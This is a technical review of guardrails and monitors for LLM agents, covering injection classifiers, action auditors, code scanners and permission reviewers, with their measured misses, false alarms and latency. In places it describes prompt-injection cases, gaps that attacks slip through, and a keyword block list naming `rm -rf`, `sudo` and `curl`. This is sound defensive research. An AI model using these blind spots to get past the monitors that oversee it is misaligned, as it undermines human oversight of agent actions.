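Adding AlignmentCheck to PromptGuard 2 stops about 58 more attacks per 1,000 attempts, but the agent completes about 43 fewer of every 1,000 ordinary tasks. Adding the PromptGuard 2 classifier to AlignmentCheck stops only 11 more attacks per 1,000, but the agent completes only 4 fewer tasks. The classifier is also much faster than AlignmentCheck, so a team that already runs AlignmentCheck has little reason not to add it.

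The decision to add AlignmentCheck to PromptGuard 2 is harder, because it makes the agent fail some tasks whether or not anyone attacks. If 1 task in 100 contained an injection like these, AlignmentCheck would prevent fewer than one extra successful attack per 1,000 tasks while causing about 43 of those tasks to fail. That could be a good trade-off for an agent that moves money but a bad one for an agent that drafts newsletters. Meta recommends the full check for agents that handle sensitive data or critical actions, and is looking into running it only when the stakes are high.

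The two parts tend to miss different attacks, but their misses overlap somewhat. If the misses were independent, 7.0% of the successful attacks would get past both parts, but the measured share was 9.9%. The correlation is about 0.16, between Yang's medians for rules paired with a language model (0.014) and for two language models (0.43). An intermediate value makes sense because both parts of LlamaFirewall use language models but look at different text.

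AlignmentCheck's false positive rate also looks much worse on AgentDojo, where it flagged 9.7% of the successful runs without an attack, than on Meta's own scenarios, where the rate was 2.5%. This may be because an AgentDojo run fails if the auditor flags any step, whereas the published example from Meta's scenarios has one verdict per auditor, on a single action. A false positive rate of 2.5% per action becomes 9.6% over four actions if errors are independent. The share of sessions that AlignmentCheck interrupts should keep growing as sessions get longer.

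Replaying stored traces also leaves out some of what would happen in real use. A flag counts as prevention even if it comes after the harmful action, so the attack figures may overstate the protection. The task figures may understate how often an agent would finish its task, because a live agent could drop a flagged page or try another action.

### CodeShield

CodeShield is a pattern scanner for code. Some of its rules are regular expressions, and others use Semgrep, which matches the structure of code, so changes in spacing or variable names don't affect the match. The rules cover more than 50 entries in the Common Weakness Enumeration, a standard catalogue of software flaws.

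In Meta's example, a coding agent copies a database query from a popular web post. The query pastes user input straight into a command, so an attacker could insert their own commands. There is no injected instruction for PromptGuard 2 to detect, and the user asked for the query, so AlignmentCheck would have nothing to flag either. CodeShield rejects the code because of the unsafe pattern, and the agent rewrites it until it passes.

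CodeShield looks for flaws in code, which is different from stopping dangerous actions. A well-written script can still post a `.env` file to an outside server, and CodeShield would probably pass it unless a developer had added a rule for that case. Chennabasappa and colleagues list malicious code execution and unsafe tool use among the risks they plan to cover later.

CodeShield has two tiers because analyzing every piece of code thoroughly would take too long. The first tier uses light pattern matching, takes about 60 milliseconds, and settles about 90% of inputs in Meta's production systems. It flags the remaining 10% for a deeper analysis that takes about 300 milliseconds. The average scan therefore takes around 90 milliseconds, compared with 360 if both tiers ran on everything. However, if the first tier fails to flag insecure code, that code never gets the deeper analysis.

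Reviewers hand-labelled 50 samples of model-written code in each of several languages to measure CodeShield's accuracy. CodeShield found 79% of the insecure samples, and 96% of its flags were correct. This precision would be lower in a codebase with fewer flaws.

### Results on other data

PromptGuard 2's recall was much lower than 97.5% on other kinds of attack. *Defusing Explosive Prompts* tested the larger model, as released, on 8,002 new texts, which included attacks planted in material such as Wikipedia articles. At the default threshold, the model caught only 13.6% of the attacks, with a false positive rate of 0.08%. Its AUROC was 0.93, so it usually scored attacks higher than harmless texts, but most attacks scored below the threshold.

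A developer can lower the threshold or train the classifier further, but either change needs testing on the text the agent will encounter. In *Defusing Explosive Prompts*, further training recovered most of the missing recall. It also raised the false positive rate on Wikipedia articles from 0% to 47%, while the rate on every other source stayed at or below 3%. An average over all the sources would have greatly understated the false positive rate for an agent that reads Wikipedia.

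Mozilla.ai's documentation page *Prompt Guard* reports similarly uneven results from the organisation's own tests. PromptGuard 2 caught 97.3% of the attacks in Gandalf, a collection of prompts from a game in which people try to trick a model into revealing a password. On another public set, from the company deepset, its F1 score, which combines precision and recall, was only 0.235. If every flag was correct, that means it caught about 13% of the attacks. On NotInject, a set of harmless prompts containing words common in attacks, it wrongly flagged 3.2%.

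A likely cause of the drop is that Meta built its benchmark around explicit jailbreak techniques, the one kind of attack PromptGuard 2 is designed to catch. An injection that politely asks for something harmful may not use any of these techniques. Another common cause of such drops is that developers test a classifier on the same datasets they trained it on. Fomin (2026), in *When Benchmarks Lie*, measured this effect on probes, which are small classifiers that take a language model's internal activations as input. Standard tests gave an AUROC 8.0 to 16.5 points higher than tests on datasets the probes had never seen. This cause is less likely here because Meta kept its training and test datasets apart.

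Fomin also found that PromptGuard 2 did worse than the probes on indirect and agent-specific attacks at the same false positive rate. Fomin works for Zenity, a security company, and designed the probes. The probes need access to the internals of the agent's model, which customers of a closed model don't have.

AlignmentCheck's results held up better, at least on AgentDojo. *Taxonomy, Evaluation and Exploitation of IPI-Centric LLM Agent Defense Frameworks* (2025) tested it with GPT-4o on AgentDojo and two other benchmarks of injection attacks, Agent Security Bench and InjecAgent. The first row repeats Meta's own result.

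| Benchmark | Model | Attack success without AlignmentCheck | With AlignmentCheck |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo (Meta's replay) | Llama 4 Maverick | 17.6% | 2.9% |
| AgentDojo | GPT-4o | 15.6% | 1.7% |
| Agent Security Bench | GPT-4o | 31.0% | 13.8% |
| InjecAgent | GPT-4o | 2.7% | 0.1% |

The reduction on AgentDojo was 89%, slightly better than Meta's, but on Agent Security Bench it was only 56%. In one failure, a user asked for a comparison of investment portfolios and an injection made the agent try to create an account. The auditor classed this as not directly serving the request, but approved it on the grounds that the account might give access to useful data. The prompt's instruction to let doubtful actions pass may have contributed, since an attacker then only has to choose an action that could conceivably help with the request.

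Task success on AgentDojo fell less than in Meta's replay, from 80.4% to 77.3%, a net loss of three tasks out of 97. AlignmentCheck raised no false alarms on the workspace and travel tasks, but its false positive rate was 6.7% on banking tasks and 15% on Slack tasks. On average, tasks took 2.8 times as long and used twice as many tokens. Slack tasks took more than five times as long.

AlignmentCheck caught more attacks with a newer model as the auditor. In *Cross-Layer Semantic Flow Reconstruction for Attack Detection in Agentic Systems*, Cai, Wei and colleagues (2026) ran it with GPT-5.6 Sol on 645 stored AgentDojo traces, all containing the "important instructions" attack. It flagged 284 of the 288 traces in which the attack had succeeded (98.6% recall) and 35 of the 357 in which it had failed (9.8%). Those 35 count as false positives, though some of the agents may have begun to follow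 the injection before giving up, which an auditor should flag. Because every trace contained an attack, the test doesn't show how often AlignmentCheck would interrupt work when there is none. Cai and colleagues were comparing AlignmentCheck with their own detector, which had the same recall but a false positive rate of 22.7%, so they had no motive to make AlignmentCheck look good.

AgentDojo has become an easier test since Meta's experiment. *aiAuthZ* (2026) tested two current models against the "important instructions" attack on 20 pairs of banking tasks and injections. Without a defence, the attack never succeeded. With the benchmark's built-in "spotlighting" defence, which marks off untrusted text, it succeeded twice against one model. Adding AlignmentCheck to undefended models like these could only reduce the number of tasks they completed on this part of the benchmark. The attacks are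 also easy to filter. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) reports that another filter for tool output missed only 0.47% of AgentDojo's attacks and had no false positives. Good results on AgentDojo are therefore weak evidence that a defence would stop an attacker who writes new text for each target.

There are few independent tests of CodeShield. *Poison with Style* (2026) found that CodeShield detected none of the vulnerable code in three classes of weakness and 75% in a fourth, but the code came from a model the researchers had deliberately corrupted. *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* (2026) tested static analysis more broadly, though it used Semgrep on its own, without CodeShield's rules. On BaxBench, which tests web applications by attacking them, Semgrep flagged 32.4% of the exploitable applications written by DeepSeek-V4.1-flash. Across the study, Semgrep's flags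 were barely better than chance at identifying insecure code.

This is far below CodeShield's 79% recall. The choice of rules may explain part of the gap, and how each test defined insecure code probably matters too. Meta's reviewers labelled code by looking for insecure patterns, which is also how the rules work. BaxBench counts an application as insecure if an exploit succeeds. Many exploits succeed because the code is missing a check, such as a permission check, which leaves no suspicious line for a pattern to match.

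## Small open models trained to judge agent actions

AlignmentCheck needs to run on a large model, because the small Llama models that Meta tried flagged too much legitimate work. Meta had not trained those models to judge actions, but other developers have released small models trained to do so. Like AlignmentCheck, these models take the user's request and the agent's history as input, so in principle they can tell a deletion the user wants from one the user doesn't. They are also small enough for a team to run on its own hardware.

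### auto-0.4b and three rivals on one test set

The smallest of these models, auto-0.4b, has 396 million parameters. It is an encoder, which reads a text in one pass and outputs a score rather than text. According to its documentation page, ProCreations' *auto-0.4b*, the model takes as input the proposed tool call, then the user's request, then the agent's earlier actions and their results. The input can be up to 64,000 tokens long, compared with 512 for PromptGuard 2. The score is the probability that the call should be denied, and the default threshold is 50%.

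ProCreations compared the model with three other systems on 3,000 proposed tool calls, of which about 1,400 should have been denied.

| System | Dangerous actions approved | Harmless actions denied | Time per call |
|---|---|---|---|
| auto-0.4b | 8.71% | 10.88% | 7 ms |
| Regular expressions | 59.39% | 26.83% | about 0 ms |
| GPT-5.6-Luna | 4.93% | 1.38% | 3.09 s |
| DeepSeek V4 Flash | 10.11% | 0.63% | 5.64 s |

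The small model is about 400 times faster than GPT-5.6-Luna, a general-purpose model that ProCreations reached over the internet, but it makes more errors of both kinds. In a session of 200 harmless actions, it would wrongly deny about 22, compared with about 3 for Luna. ProCreations acknowledges this and does not recommend the model as a replacement for a large one.

The regular expressions are a weak baseline. They block any call that contains a string such as `rm -rf`, `sudo` or `curl`, but about half of the dangerous calls in the test contain no such string, and many of the harmless ones contain several. A careful rule set like AgentTrust's would probably have done better, so the comparison mainly shows that a crude keyword list is inadequate.

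One developer built the model, the test set and the keyword baseline, and wrote the report. DeepSeek V4 Flash generated the 73,509 training examples, which cover different agent products, types of risk, languages and ways of disguising a command. Many come in pairs of nearly identical calls with opposite labels, where only the user's request or the history differs. For example, deleting a build folder is fine if the user asked for a clean build but wrong if they asked for a list of files. Such pairs force a classifier to use the context instead of the command's wording.

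ProCreations checked the test labels in a second pass, but used a model from the same family as the first, so both could make the same mistakes. A release of DeepSeek V4 Flash, which is also one of the systems compared, approved about a tenth of the calls labelled dangerous, so the labels do not simply repeat its own verdicts. The bigger concern is that auto-0.4b was trained on synthetic examples much like those in the test, so it could make more errors on real sessions, as CloneGuard's classifier did on unfamiliar text.

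The classifier made more errors on the test's longer histories. On items with fewer than 1,000 tokens, which make up four in five of the test items, it approved 7.4% of the dangerous calls and denied 9.6% of the harmless ones. On the 232 items with 16,000 to 64,000 tokens, those rates were 25.6% and 17.1%. A coding agent's history can reach that length after the agent reads a few large files. Passing the classifier only the latest steps would keep the input short, but it would also hide any earlier step that makes the current one dangerous.

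The error rate also varies with the type of danger. The model approved only 1% to 3% of calls in five categories that ProCreations singles out: disabling the agent's own guardrails, covering tracks, following injected instructions, gaining extra privileges and stealing credentials. Since the overall rate is 8.71%, the remaining categories must average more than that.

### Escalating from the small model to a large one

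A team could use auto-0.4b to settle most actions and call Luna only for some of them. Suppose that Luna reviews every action the small model denies and can overrule it. If their errors are independent, the figures above give:

- false positives: 0.1088 × 0.0138 = 0.15%
- false negatives: 1 − (0.9129 × 0.9507) = 13.2%
- mean delay on harmless actions: 7 ms + (0.1088 × 3,090 ms) = 343 ms

This pair would be pleasant to use because it would deny only about 1 harmless action in 670 and delay most actions by only 7 ms. But it would miss more dangerous actions than either model alone. The small model approves 8.71% of dangerous actions, which Luna never receives, and Luna wrongly allows 4.93% of those the small model catches.

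If Luna instead reviews what the small model approves, an action runs only if both models approve it. False negatives fall to 0.43% and false positives rise to 12.1%. The mean delay on harmless actions rises to 2.76 seconds, because most of them now go to Luna.

Reviewing only denials can therefore add wrong approvals but not wrong denials, and reviewing only approvals does the reverse. If Luna ran first and the small model reviewed its denials, the error rates would still be 0.15% and 13.2%, because both models would still have to deny an action to stop it. But every action would wait about three seconds for Luna.

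A third option is to lower the small model's threshold from 50% to 10%. It then approves only 2.71% of dangerous actions but denies 26.83% of harmless ones. That denial rate would be intolerable if the model were used alone, but Luna can clear most of the extra denials. ProCreations recommends using two thresholds, so that the model approves low-scoring actions, denies high-scoring ones and sends the rest to a larger model. The last row of this table uses thresholds of 10% and 90%. All the combined figures assume independent errors.

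| Arrangement | False negatives | False positives | Mean delay, harmless actions |
|---|---|---|---|
| auto-0.4b alone | 8.7% | 10.9% | 0.007 s |
| Luna alone | 4.9% | 1.4% | 3.09 s |
| Luna reviews denials, threshold 50% | 13.2% | 0.15% | 0.34 s |
| Luna reviews denials, threshold 10% | 7.5% | 0.37% | 0.84 s |
| Luna reviews approvals, threshold 50% | 0.43% | 12.1% | 2.76 s |
| Luna reviews scores from 10% to 90% | 3.5% | 4.5% | 0.71 s |

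Lowering the threshold nearly halves the first arrangement's false negatives and adds half a second of delay. If a larger model can only overrule denials, the small model should have a low threshold for denying actions.

The last row shows fewer false negatives than Luna alone, but that result is probably too optimistic. The actions with middling scores are the ones the small model found hardest, and Luna may find them hard too. If all of Luna's misses were in that group, the false negative rate would be 7.6%. Correlation between the two models' errors would lower the 13.2% figure, but by a smaller amount. If Luna missed only actions that the small model also missed, that rate would fall to 8.7%. It can't go lower because Luna never reviews the actions the small model misses.

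How these options compare also depends on how rare dangerous actions are. When 1 action in 1,000 is dangerous, only about 1 in 120 of auto-0.4b's denials is correct. If Luna reviews the denials, more than a third of the remaining ones are correct. That makes a denial worth a user's attention, but the pair lets through more dangerous actions than auto-0.4b alone.

### ToolSafe: judging one step before it runs

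In *ToolSafe*, Mou, Xue and colleagues (2026) trained a larger model, TS-Guard, that also checks each tool call before it runs. They started from Qwen2.5-7B-Instruct, an open model with 7 billion parameters. TS-Guard takes the user's request, the earlier steps, the proposed call and descriptions of the available tools. It writes a short analysis, then judges whether the request is harmful, whether the proposed call is connected to an injection, and whether the call is safe, controversial or unsafe.

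Mou and colleagues used reinforcement learning with a training set of only 2,193 steps. The model writes 16 answers to each example, and training makes the better ones more likely. Each answer starts with a reward of 1 and loses a third of a point for each of the three questions it gets wrong. Rewarding only the final safety rating gave lower F1 scores and more false positives.

The test of TS-Guard used steps from three benchmarks. AgentHarm contains harmful requests from the user, while Agent Security Bench and AgentDojo contain injections. The training data included three of the ten subject areas in Agent Security Bench, but no steps from AgentHarm or AgentDojo. The test used the other seven areas. Each cell below gives the share of unsafe steps missed, then the share of safe steps flagged. "Controversial" counts as unsafe, and the second figure is calculated from the published accuracy,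 recall and sample sizes.

| Model | AgentHarm | Agent Security Bench | AgentDojo |
|---|---|---|---|
| TS-Guard | 3% / 46% | 6% / 4% | 11% / 7% |
| GPT-4o | 4% / 78% | 40% / 29% | 0% / 62% |
| Llama Guard 3 (8B) | 19% / 18% | 85% / 8% | 78% / 4% |
| Qwen3Guard (8B) | 15% / 31% | 92% / 3% | 98% / 1% |

Llama Guard and Qwen3Guard are safeguard models for chat, trained to recognise harmful content. They do reasonably well on AgentHarm, where the request itself is harmful, but they miss most of the injected actions on AgentDojo, where the agent might send an ordinary email or payment that the user never asked for. GPT-4o caught every injected action on AgentDojo but also flagged most of the safe steps, apparently because an injection elsewhere in the history was enough to trigger a flag.

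TS-Guard avoided both failures on AgentDojo, which is good evidence that a small amount of suitable training helps. It was weakest on AgentHarm, where it flagged 95 of 206 safe steps. In the part of the training data most similar to AgentHarm, only 123 of 673 steps were safe, so training may have made the model too likely to flag steps in tasks of that kind.

If TS-Guard blocks only actions it rates "unsafe" and allows those it rates "controversial", its false positive rate on AgentDojo falls from 7% to 0.8%, but its miss rate rises from 11% to 47%. A developer could send the "controversial" actions to a larger model or a person, as with auto-0.4b's mid-range scores.

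Mou and colleagues also tested what an agent should do after a denial. LlamaFirewall ends the task, whereas their own design, TS-Flow, passes TS-Guard's analysis to the agent and lets it try again. These are the results for a GPT-4o agent under attack on AgentDojo:

| Arrangement | Attack success rate | Task success rate |
|---|---|---|
| No defence | 56.2% | 26.9% |
| TS-Guard, task ends on a denial | 1.0% | 20.8% |
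| TS-Guard, agent receives the analysis | 1.2% | 42.8% |

Both designs stopped nearly all the attacks, but the agent completed twice as many tasks when it could continue. It even completed more than it did without a defence, because an undefended agent often left the user's task to pursue the attacker's. In a test with a Qwen agent on Agent Security Bench, attacks succeeded 7% of the time when the agent received the full analysis as feedback and 26% when it received only the safety rating. Explaining a denial therefore helps prevent attacks, although the analysis also made the agent's input 36% to 89% longer on AgentDojo.

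TS-Guard took 1.36 seconds per check on average, compared with 1.98 seconds for GPT-4o. AGrail, which uses GPT-4o to work through a checklist, took 8.75 seconds and was less accurate than TS-Guard on both benchmarks where they were compared.

### AgentDoG 1.5: judging the whole trace before the reply

*AgentDoG 1.5* (Liu, Shao and colleagues, 2026) instead presents models that judge a complete trace, including every action and result, as safe or unsafe. The models have 0.8, 2, 4 or 8 billion parameters. Separate versions also identify the source of the risk, the agent's mistake and the resulting harm. The project comes from the Shanghai Artificial Intelligence Laboratory, which also took part in ToolSafe.

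Liu and colleagues generated a large pool of synthetic traces. For each trace they drew a risk from their list of categories, and a planning model then devised a task and the point where the risk would enter it. GPT-5.4 then wrote a reasoned judgement for each training example. The final training set had only about 1,000 examples, which they selected with this score:

score(z) = g(z) · G

Here g(z) is the gradient of the model's training loss on example z, which describes how that loss changes with the model's parameters. G is the average difference between the gradients for correct and incorrect judgements on a small set of target cases, with more weight on cases the model already tends to get right. A high score means training on z should make correct judgements more likely relative to incorrect ones.

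The main test, ATBench, has 503 safe traces and 497 unsafe ones. These error rates follow from the published accuracy and recall.

| Model | Unsafe traces missed | Safe traces flagged |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDoG 1.5, 0.8B | 31% | 48% |
| AgentDoG 1.5, 4B | 20% | 35% |
| AgentDoG 1.5, 4B, trained on both tasks | 24% | 19% |
| GPT-5.4 | 13% | 40% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 29% | 18% |

The 4B models perform similarly to much larger ones, as Liu and colleagues claim. But all five models make many errors, and a monitor that flags between a fifth and a half of safe traces would be hard to use in practice. The model trained on both tasks flagged far fewer safe traces than the ordinary 4B version, so training it to name the risk probably also made it better at detecting whether there was one.

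ATBench scores are hard to compare across papers. *AgentDoG* (2026), which introduced the previous version, reports 92.8% accuracy on ATBench for its 4B model. *AgentDoG 1.5* reports 64.0% for what appears to be the same model. Both papers report 91.8% for it on another benchmark, R-Judge, so ATBench may have become harder between the two papers.

In use, AgentDoG 1.5 runs once per task, just before the agent's final reply reaches the user. Liu and colleagues chose this point because checking every call would slow long tasks, and because agent products offer different hooks but nearly all have a final reply. By then the agent's actions have already taken effect, so the check can stop a reply that reveals a password but can't prevent a deletion or recall an email. Liu and colleagues acknowledge this and recommend adding selective checks on tool calls, permission rules and human approval for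 risky actions.

They tested the check on OpenClaw, an open-source agent that works across a user's applications, and kept only cases where blocking the reply could still prevent the harm. The table shows how many unsafe replies reached the user.

| Guard | ClawSafety (16 cases) | AgentHazard (260) | CIK-Bench (35) |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 9 | 109 | 33 |
| Llama Guard 3, 8B | 4 | 109 | 14 |
| Qwen3Guard, 4B | 7 | 109 | 32 |
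| AgentDoG 1.5, 0.8B | 4 | 76 | 30 |
| AgentDoG 1.5, 4B | 3 | 70 | 15 |

AgentDoG's clearest gain over the chat safeguards is on AgentHazard, where unsafe replies disclose hidden prompts or details of the agent's tools. The chat safeguards blocked none of the 109 unsafe replies, presumably because such text is not harmful in the usual sense. The best AgentDoG model blocked only 39. On CIK-Bench, where unsafe replies reveal private content or contain dangerous strings, Llama Guard did slightly better than AgentDoG's 4B model. The test counted only unsafe replies, so it does not measure the false positive rate on harmless tasks.

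*AgentDoG 1.5* also claims to reduce deployment overhead by two orders of magnitude. This refers to the simulated environments in which the team trains other agents, with AgentDoG scoring their behaviour for safety. Developers often run such environments in Docker containers, which package a whole software system. Liu and colleagues replaced them with small Python programs that imitate only the tools and files a task needs. By their account, these programs use a hundredth of the memory that Docker does and start in a hundredth of the time. They measured 10,000 of these environments fitting in less than 2.5 GB of memory, but did not run Docker for comparison. The saving applies to training and does not affect how long a user waits for a verdict.

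### How an untrained judge compares

Training a special model is worthwhile only if it improves on prompting a general one. In *CAITLYN*, Liang, Xu and colleagues (2026) ran a prompted general model as a baseline for their own defence, testing it with five agents: OpenCode, Codex, Pi, Hermes and OpenClaw. The baseline makes one model call with a text-classification prompt, and it looks for injections in what the agent reads, not for dangerous actions. The ranges below cover all five agents, except that the AgentDojo cost leaves out OpenClaw, for which they give no figure.

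| | AgentDojo | ASPI | SafeClawBench |
|---|---|---|---|
| Location of the attack | tool output | user's reply to a question | user's prompt |
| Attack success, no defence | 6.8–16.8% | 5.4–19.4% | 20.0–33.3% |
| Attack success with the judge | 0–0.4% | 1.1–2.2% | 17.9–24.2% |
| False positive rate | 0% | 3.2–9.7% | not measured |
| Time per task, no defence | 7.1–14.9 s | 7.2–16.8 s | 11.7–27.1 s |
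| Time per task with the judge | 7.3–16.4 s | 5.9–12.5 s | 12.9–18.2 s |
| Cost per task with the judge | $0.0004–0.0047 | $0.0004–0.0092 | $0.0006–0.0162 |

The judge prevented more than 99% of the AgentDojo attacks that would otherwise have succeeded, 84% of those in ASPI and only 25% of those in SafeClawBench, averaged over the five agents. The location of the attack may explain much of the difference, because a command is out of place inside a web page but looks like a request in the user's own prompt. When Liang and colleagues tested detection without an agent, judges of this kind caught every AgentDojo attack and half of those in SafeClawBench.

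Liang and colleagues also built a benchmark of attacks that contain little that looks like an instruction, such as a vendor's record with altered contact details. Against every fixed defence they tested, the attacks still succeeded between 72.5% and 80% of the time. They used the benchmark to demonstrate a system that writes new rules after each failure, so they had reason to choose attacks that fixed defences miss. Even so, a judge that looks for suspicious text would clearly have trouble detecting a false phone number.

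The false positive rates on ASPI are less precise than they look. They are all multiples of 1/31, which suggests the harmless set had only 31 items. A rate of 9.7% would then be three false alarms, and 3.2% would be one.

The times cover whole tasks, so they are a poor measure of the delay the judge adds. Codex took 27.1 seconds per SafeClawBench task without a defence and 18.2 seconds with the judge, probably because a blocked task ends early. The costs include the agent's own model calls, so they are also a poor measure of what the judge costs.

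Such results can be very sensitive to the test set-up. In the same experiment, Liang and colleagues ran a small classifier, Protect AI's ready-made injection detector, on AgentDojo's harmless tasks. It flagged 57.7% of them with OpenCode and none with the other four agents. OpenCode received the benchmark's text through a real tool connection, while at least three of the others received it as part of the prompt. That difference is the most likely explanation. If so, false alarms could also be common in ordinary use, where agents receive most of their outside text through tools.

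### Why small models are not always fast

The published response times for these models are only weakly related to their size. The AgentDoG, Llama Guard and Qwen3Guard figures below are the time to the first token plus the time to generate the rest.

| Model | Parameters | Tokens written per verdict | Time per verdict |
|---|---|---|---|
| auto-0.4b | 0.4 billion | none | 0.007 s |
| Llama Guard 3 | 8 billion | 3–4 | 0.08–0.14 s |
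| Qwen3Guard | 4 billion | 8–14 | 0.18–0.29 s |
| TS-Guard | 7 billion | about 200 | 1.36 s |
| AgentDoG 1.5 | 0.8 billion | 305–367 | 4.6–5.6 s |
| AgentDoG 1.5 | 4 billion | 377–493 | 7.9–10.5 s |

The smallest AgentDoG model has a tenth of Llama Guard's parameters but takes about 40 times as long, because it writes an analysis, one token at a time, before its verdict. Liu and colleagues point out that the first token arrives in under a second, but the software can't act until the verdict arrives. A wait of eight or ten seconds may be acceptable once per task, but it would add about three minutes if repeated before each of 20 tool calls.

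The written analysis gave the agent in the ToolSafe experiment information it could use, and a person can read it when a verdict looks wrong. A team that wants both speed and explanations could let an encoder approve most actions and request an analysis only before a denial, so harmless actions would rarely have to wait for one.

The timings in the table come from different hardware and inputs, so only the large gaps are meaningful. Artificial Analysis' *Benchmarking guardrail models for safety, refusal, and latency* describes a more careful procedure, though for chat safeguards. The company, which compares AI models, ran nearly all the safeguards on the same class of data-centre GPU. It discarded 20 warm-up requests for each model, then timed 450 prompts one at a time until the full response arrived. It partnered with NVIDIA, which makes several of the models, but says it did the analysis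 independently.

None of those prompts contained tool calls, and Artificial Analysis lists tool calls and longer conversations among the topics future tests should cover. Length in particular could change the results, since a model has to read the agent's history before judging the next step. The 7 ms for auto-0.4b was measured on a test set in which most inputs had fewer than 1,000 tokens, and a session with 50,000 tokens of history would take longer to check.

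## gpt-oss-safeguard as a reviewer of permissions

TS-Guard, AgentDoG and auto-0.4b learned what counts as dangerous from labelled examples, so a team that wants a different rule has to retrain the model. gpt-oss-safeguard, an open model from OpenAI, takes the rule as part of its input, so it is a natural candidate for deciding whether an agent has permission to act. A harmless refund that the customer asked for can still be forbidden because the agent's authority to issue refunds ended yesterday.

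### A policy with every request

OpenAI's *Introducing gpt-oss-safeguard* (2025) describes a model that takes a written policy and the content to judge. The model reasons in text about how the policy applies, then outputs a label. If it blocks too much, the developer can edit the policy, and the new wording applies from the next request.

OpenAI's *User guide for gpt-oss-safeguard*, prepared with the online-safety organisation ROOST, recommends a policy in four parts: instructions, definitions, criteria for what does and doesn't violate the policy, and a few short examples near the boundary. The instructions must specify the exact form of the answer, such as 1 for a violation and 0 for none. Early tests suggested that policies of 400 to 600 tokens work best, although the model still gives reasonable results at about 10,000. One request can include several policies, but this slightly reduces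 accuracy.

The model comes in two sizes, both under the Apache 2.0 licence, which permits commercial use and modification. The smaller has 21 billion parameters, 3.6 billion of them active at a time, and fits on a graphics card with 16 GB of memory, according to OpenAI's documentation page *gpt-oss-safeguard-20b*. The larger has 117 billion parameters, 5.1 billion of them active, and needs an H100 data-centre card, according to OpenAI's *gpt-oss-safeguard-120b*.

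OpenAI says that classifiers trained on tens of thousands of good examples can still be more accurate than gpt-oss-safeguard, and that the model takes a lot of time and computing power. For its internal version, OpenAI uses small, fast classifiers to select the content worth reviewing, and sometimes runs the review in the background so that users don't have to wait. For an agent's actions, a background verdict could come too late, as AgentDoG's does.

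OpenAI tested gpt-oss-safeguard on content moderation, not on agent actions. In OpenAI's *Performance and baseline evaluations of gpt-oss-safeguard-120b and gpt-oss-safeguard-20b* (2025), the hardest test supplied several policies at once and counted an answer as correct only if every label was right. The 20b model scored 43.6% and the 120b model 46.3%, compared with about 32% for the models OpenAI started from and 43.2% for the much larger gpt-5-thinking. The extra training clearly helped, but both models still got at least one label wrong in more than half of cases.

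### Why a fixed list of harms can't settle permission

Qwen3Guard, one of the chat safeguards that missed most of the injected actions in the ToolSafe test, has its definition of harm built in. Qwen Team's *Qwen3Guard Technical Report* (2025) lists nine categories: violence, non-violent crime, sexual content, personal information, self-harm, unethical acts, politically sensitive topics, copyright violation and jailbreaks. The model learned them from 1.19 million examples. It rates each text as safe, controversial or unsafe, and a developer can choose whether "controversial" counts as unsafe.

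That choice makes the filter stricter or looser, but it can't add a rule about who may approve a payment. An ordinary payment fits none of the nine categories, whether or not someone approved it.

### One operation in four contexts

*Same Operation, Different Permission* (Jing, Chen and colleagues, 2026) tests whether a reviewer pays attention to permission by keeping the operation the same and changing only the evidence of permission. The language track of its benchmark, AuthorizationPairs, contains 50 operations, such as payments, software releases and updates to patient records. Each operation appears in two contexts that permit it and two that forbid it.

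One operation is a $75 refund to a customer's original card. An active delegation with a $100 limit permits it, but a revoked delegation would not. The two permitted contexts often rest on different grounds, such as a direct grant and an accepted handover from a colleague. A reviewer that always approves or always refuses gets exactly half the contexts right.

Three people with security experience independently labelled all 200 contexts. They all agreed on 186 and settled the rest by discussion. Jing and colleagues used ten operations to check that the software worked and tested on the other 40, which gives 160 inputs. If the reviewer returned "allow", the software carried out the operation in a local simulation, and a separate program confirmed the effect. Any other output stopped the operation.

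The gpt-oss-safeguard results are for the 20b version at medium reasoning effort. Qwen3.5 is a family of general-purpose models. The other systems are safeguards. NeMo self-check is a yes-or-no prompt from NVIDIA's guardrail software, run here on Qwen3.5-9B. The last column is calculated from the published totals.

| Reviewer | Forbidden operations run (of 80) | Permitted operations run (of 80) | No usable decision (of 160) | Tokens written per decision |
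|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-safeguard-20b | 0 | 80 | 0 | 297 |
| Qwen3.5-27B, with reasoning | 0 | 80 | 0 | 1,346 |
| Qwen3.5-9B | 6 | 65 | 0 | 8 |
| NeMo self-check | 14 | 72 | 0 | 2 |
| Granite Guardian | 17 | 69 | 0 | 428 |
| PolicyGuard | 47 | 46 | 67 | 4 |
| Nemotron | 58 | 76 | 12 | 1,529 |
| Qwen3Guard | 72 | 80 | 0 | 8 |

gpt-oss-safeguard made no errors, and it wrote less than a quarter as much text as the only other system with a perfect score. Qwen3Guard let through 72 of the 80 forbidden operations, even though the test counted "controversial" as a block. The eight it stopped came from five scenarios. Most of these concern the use or export of people's records, which is the closest the test comes to Qwen3Guard's own categories. Jing and colleagues included it as a control, since nobody designed it to judge permission.

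Several reviewers had trouble with permissions that can be used only once. Qwen3.5-9B was right on 75% of those inputs and Granite Guardian on 62%, lower than on nearly every other type of permission. For these inputs, a reviewer has to work out whether an earlier event, such as an interrupted download, has already used up the permission.

A perfect score on 160 inputs doesn't rule out errors. Even if the 80 forbidden inputs were independent, zero misses would be compatible with a true miss rate of up to about 3.7%. The inputs come from only 40 operations, so the uncertainty is larger than that. Jing and colleagues drafted the scenarios with AI help, and every annotator works in security, so a clinician or an accountant might read some of the policies differently. Each case also involves a single decision with the relevant evidence already collected, whereas a real agent's permission may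 depend on something that happened 50 steps earlier.

The benchmark also has no attacker who plants text to sway the reviewer. OpenAI's own tests suggest that the model could be vulnerable to this. In one chat test, a user tries to make the model say "access granted" against its system instructions. The 20b model resisted 51% of the time, compared with 64% for the gpt-oss model it was trained from, and OpenAI doesn't know why the score fell. An agent's tool call can contain text from a hostile web page, so a team would want to test for this weakness before relying on the model to approve or block actions.

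### Requests labelled by policy engines

The second track is harder. It contains 1,594 requests from public examples for OpenFGA and Cedar, two systems in which developers write access rules in a formal language. The labels come from a policy engine, a program that applies the rules to compute whether to permit a request, so they don't depend on an annotator's interpretation. The reviewer receives the rules, the request and the current facts, such as who owns which folder.

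The test set contains 1,215 of these requests, all but 34 of them from OpenFGA. Qwen3.5-27B was right on 99.1% of them, approving one forbidden request and denying ten lawful ones. gpt-oss-safeguard was right on only 84.2%. It approved 12 of the 448 forbidden requests and denied 174 of the 767 lawful ones. On another five lawful requests, it hit its output limit before deciding. If those five count as denials, its false positive rate was 23.3% and its false negative rate 2.7%.

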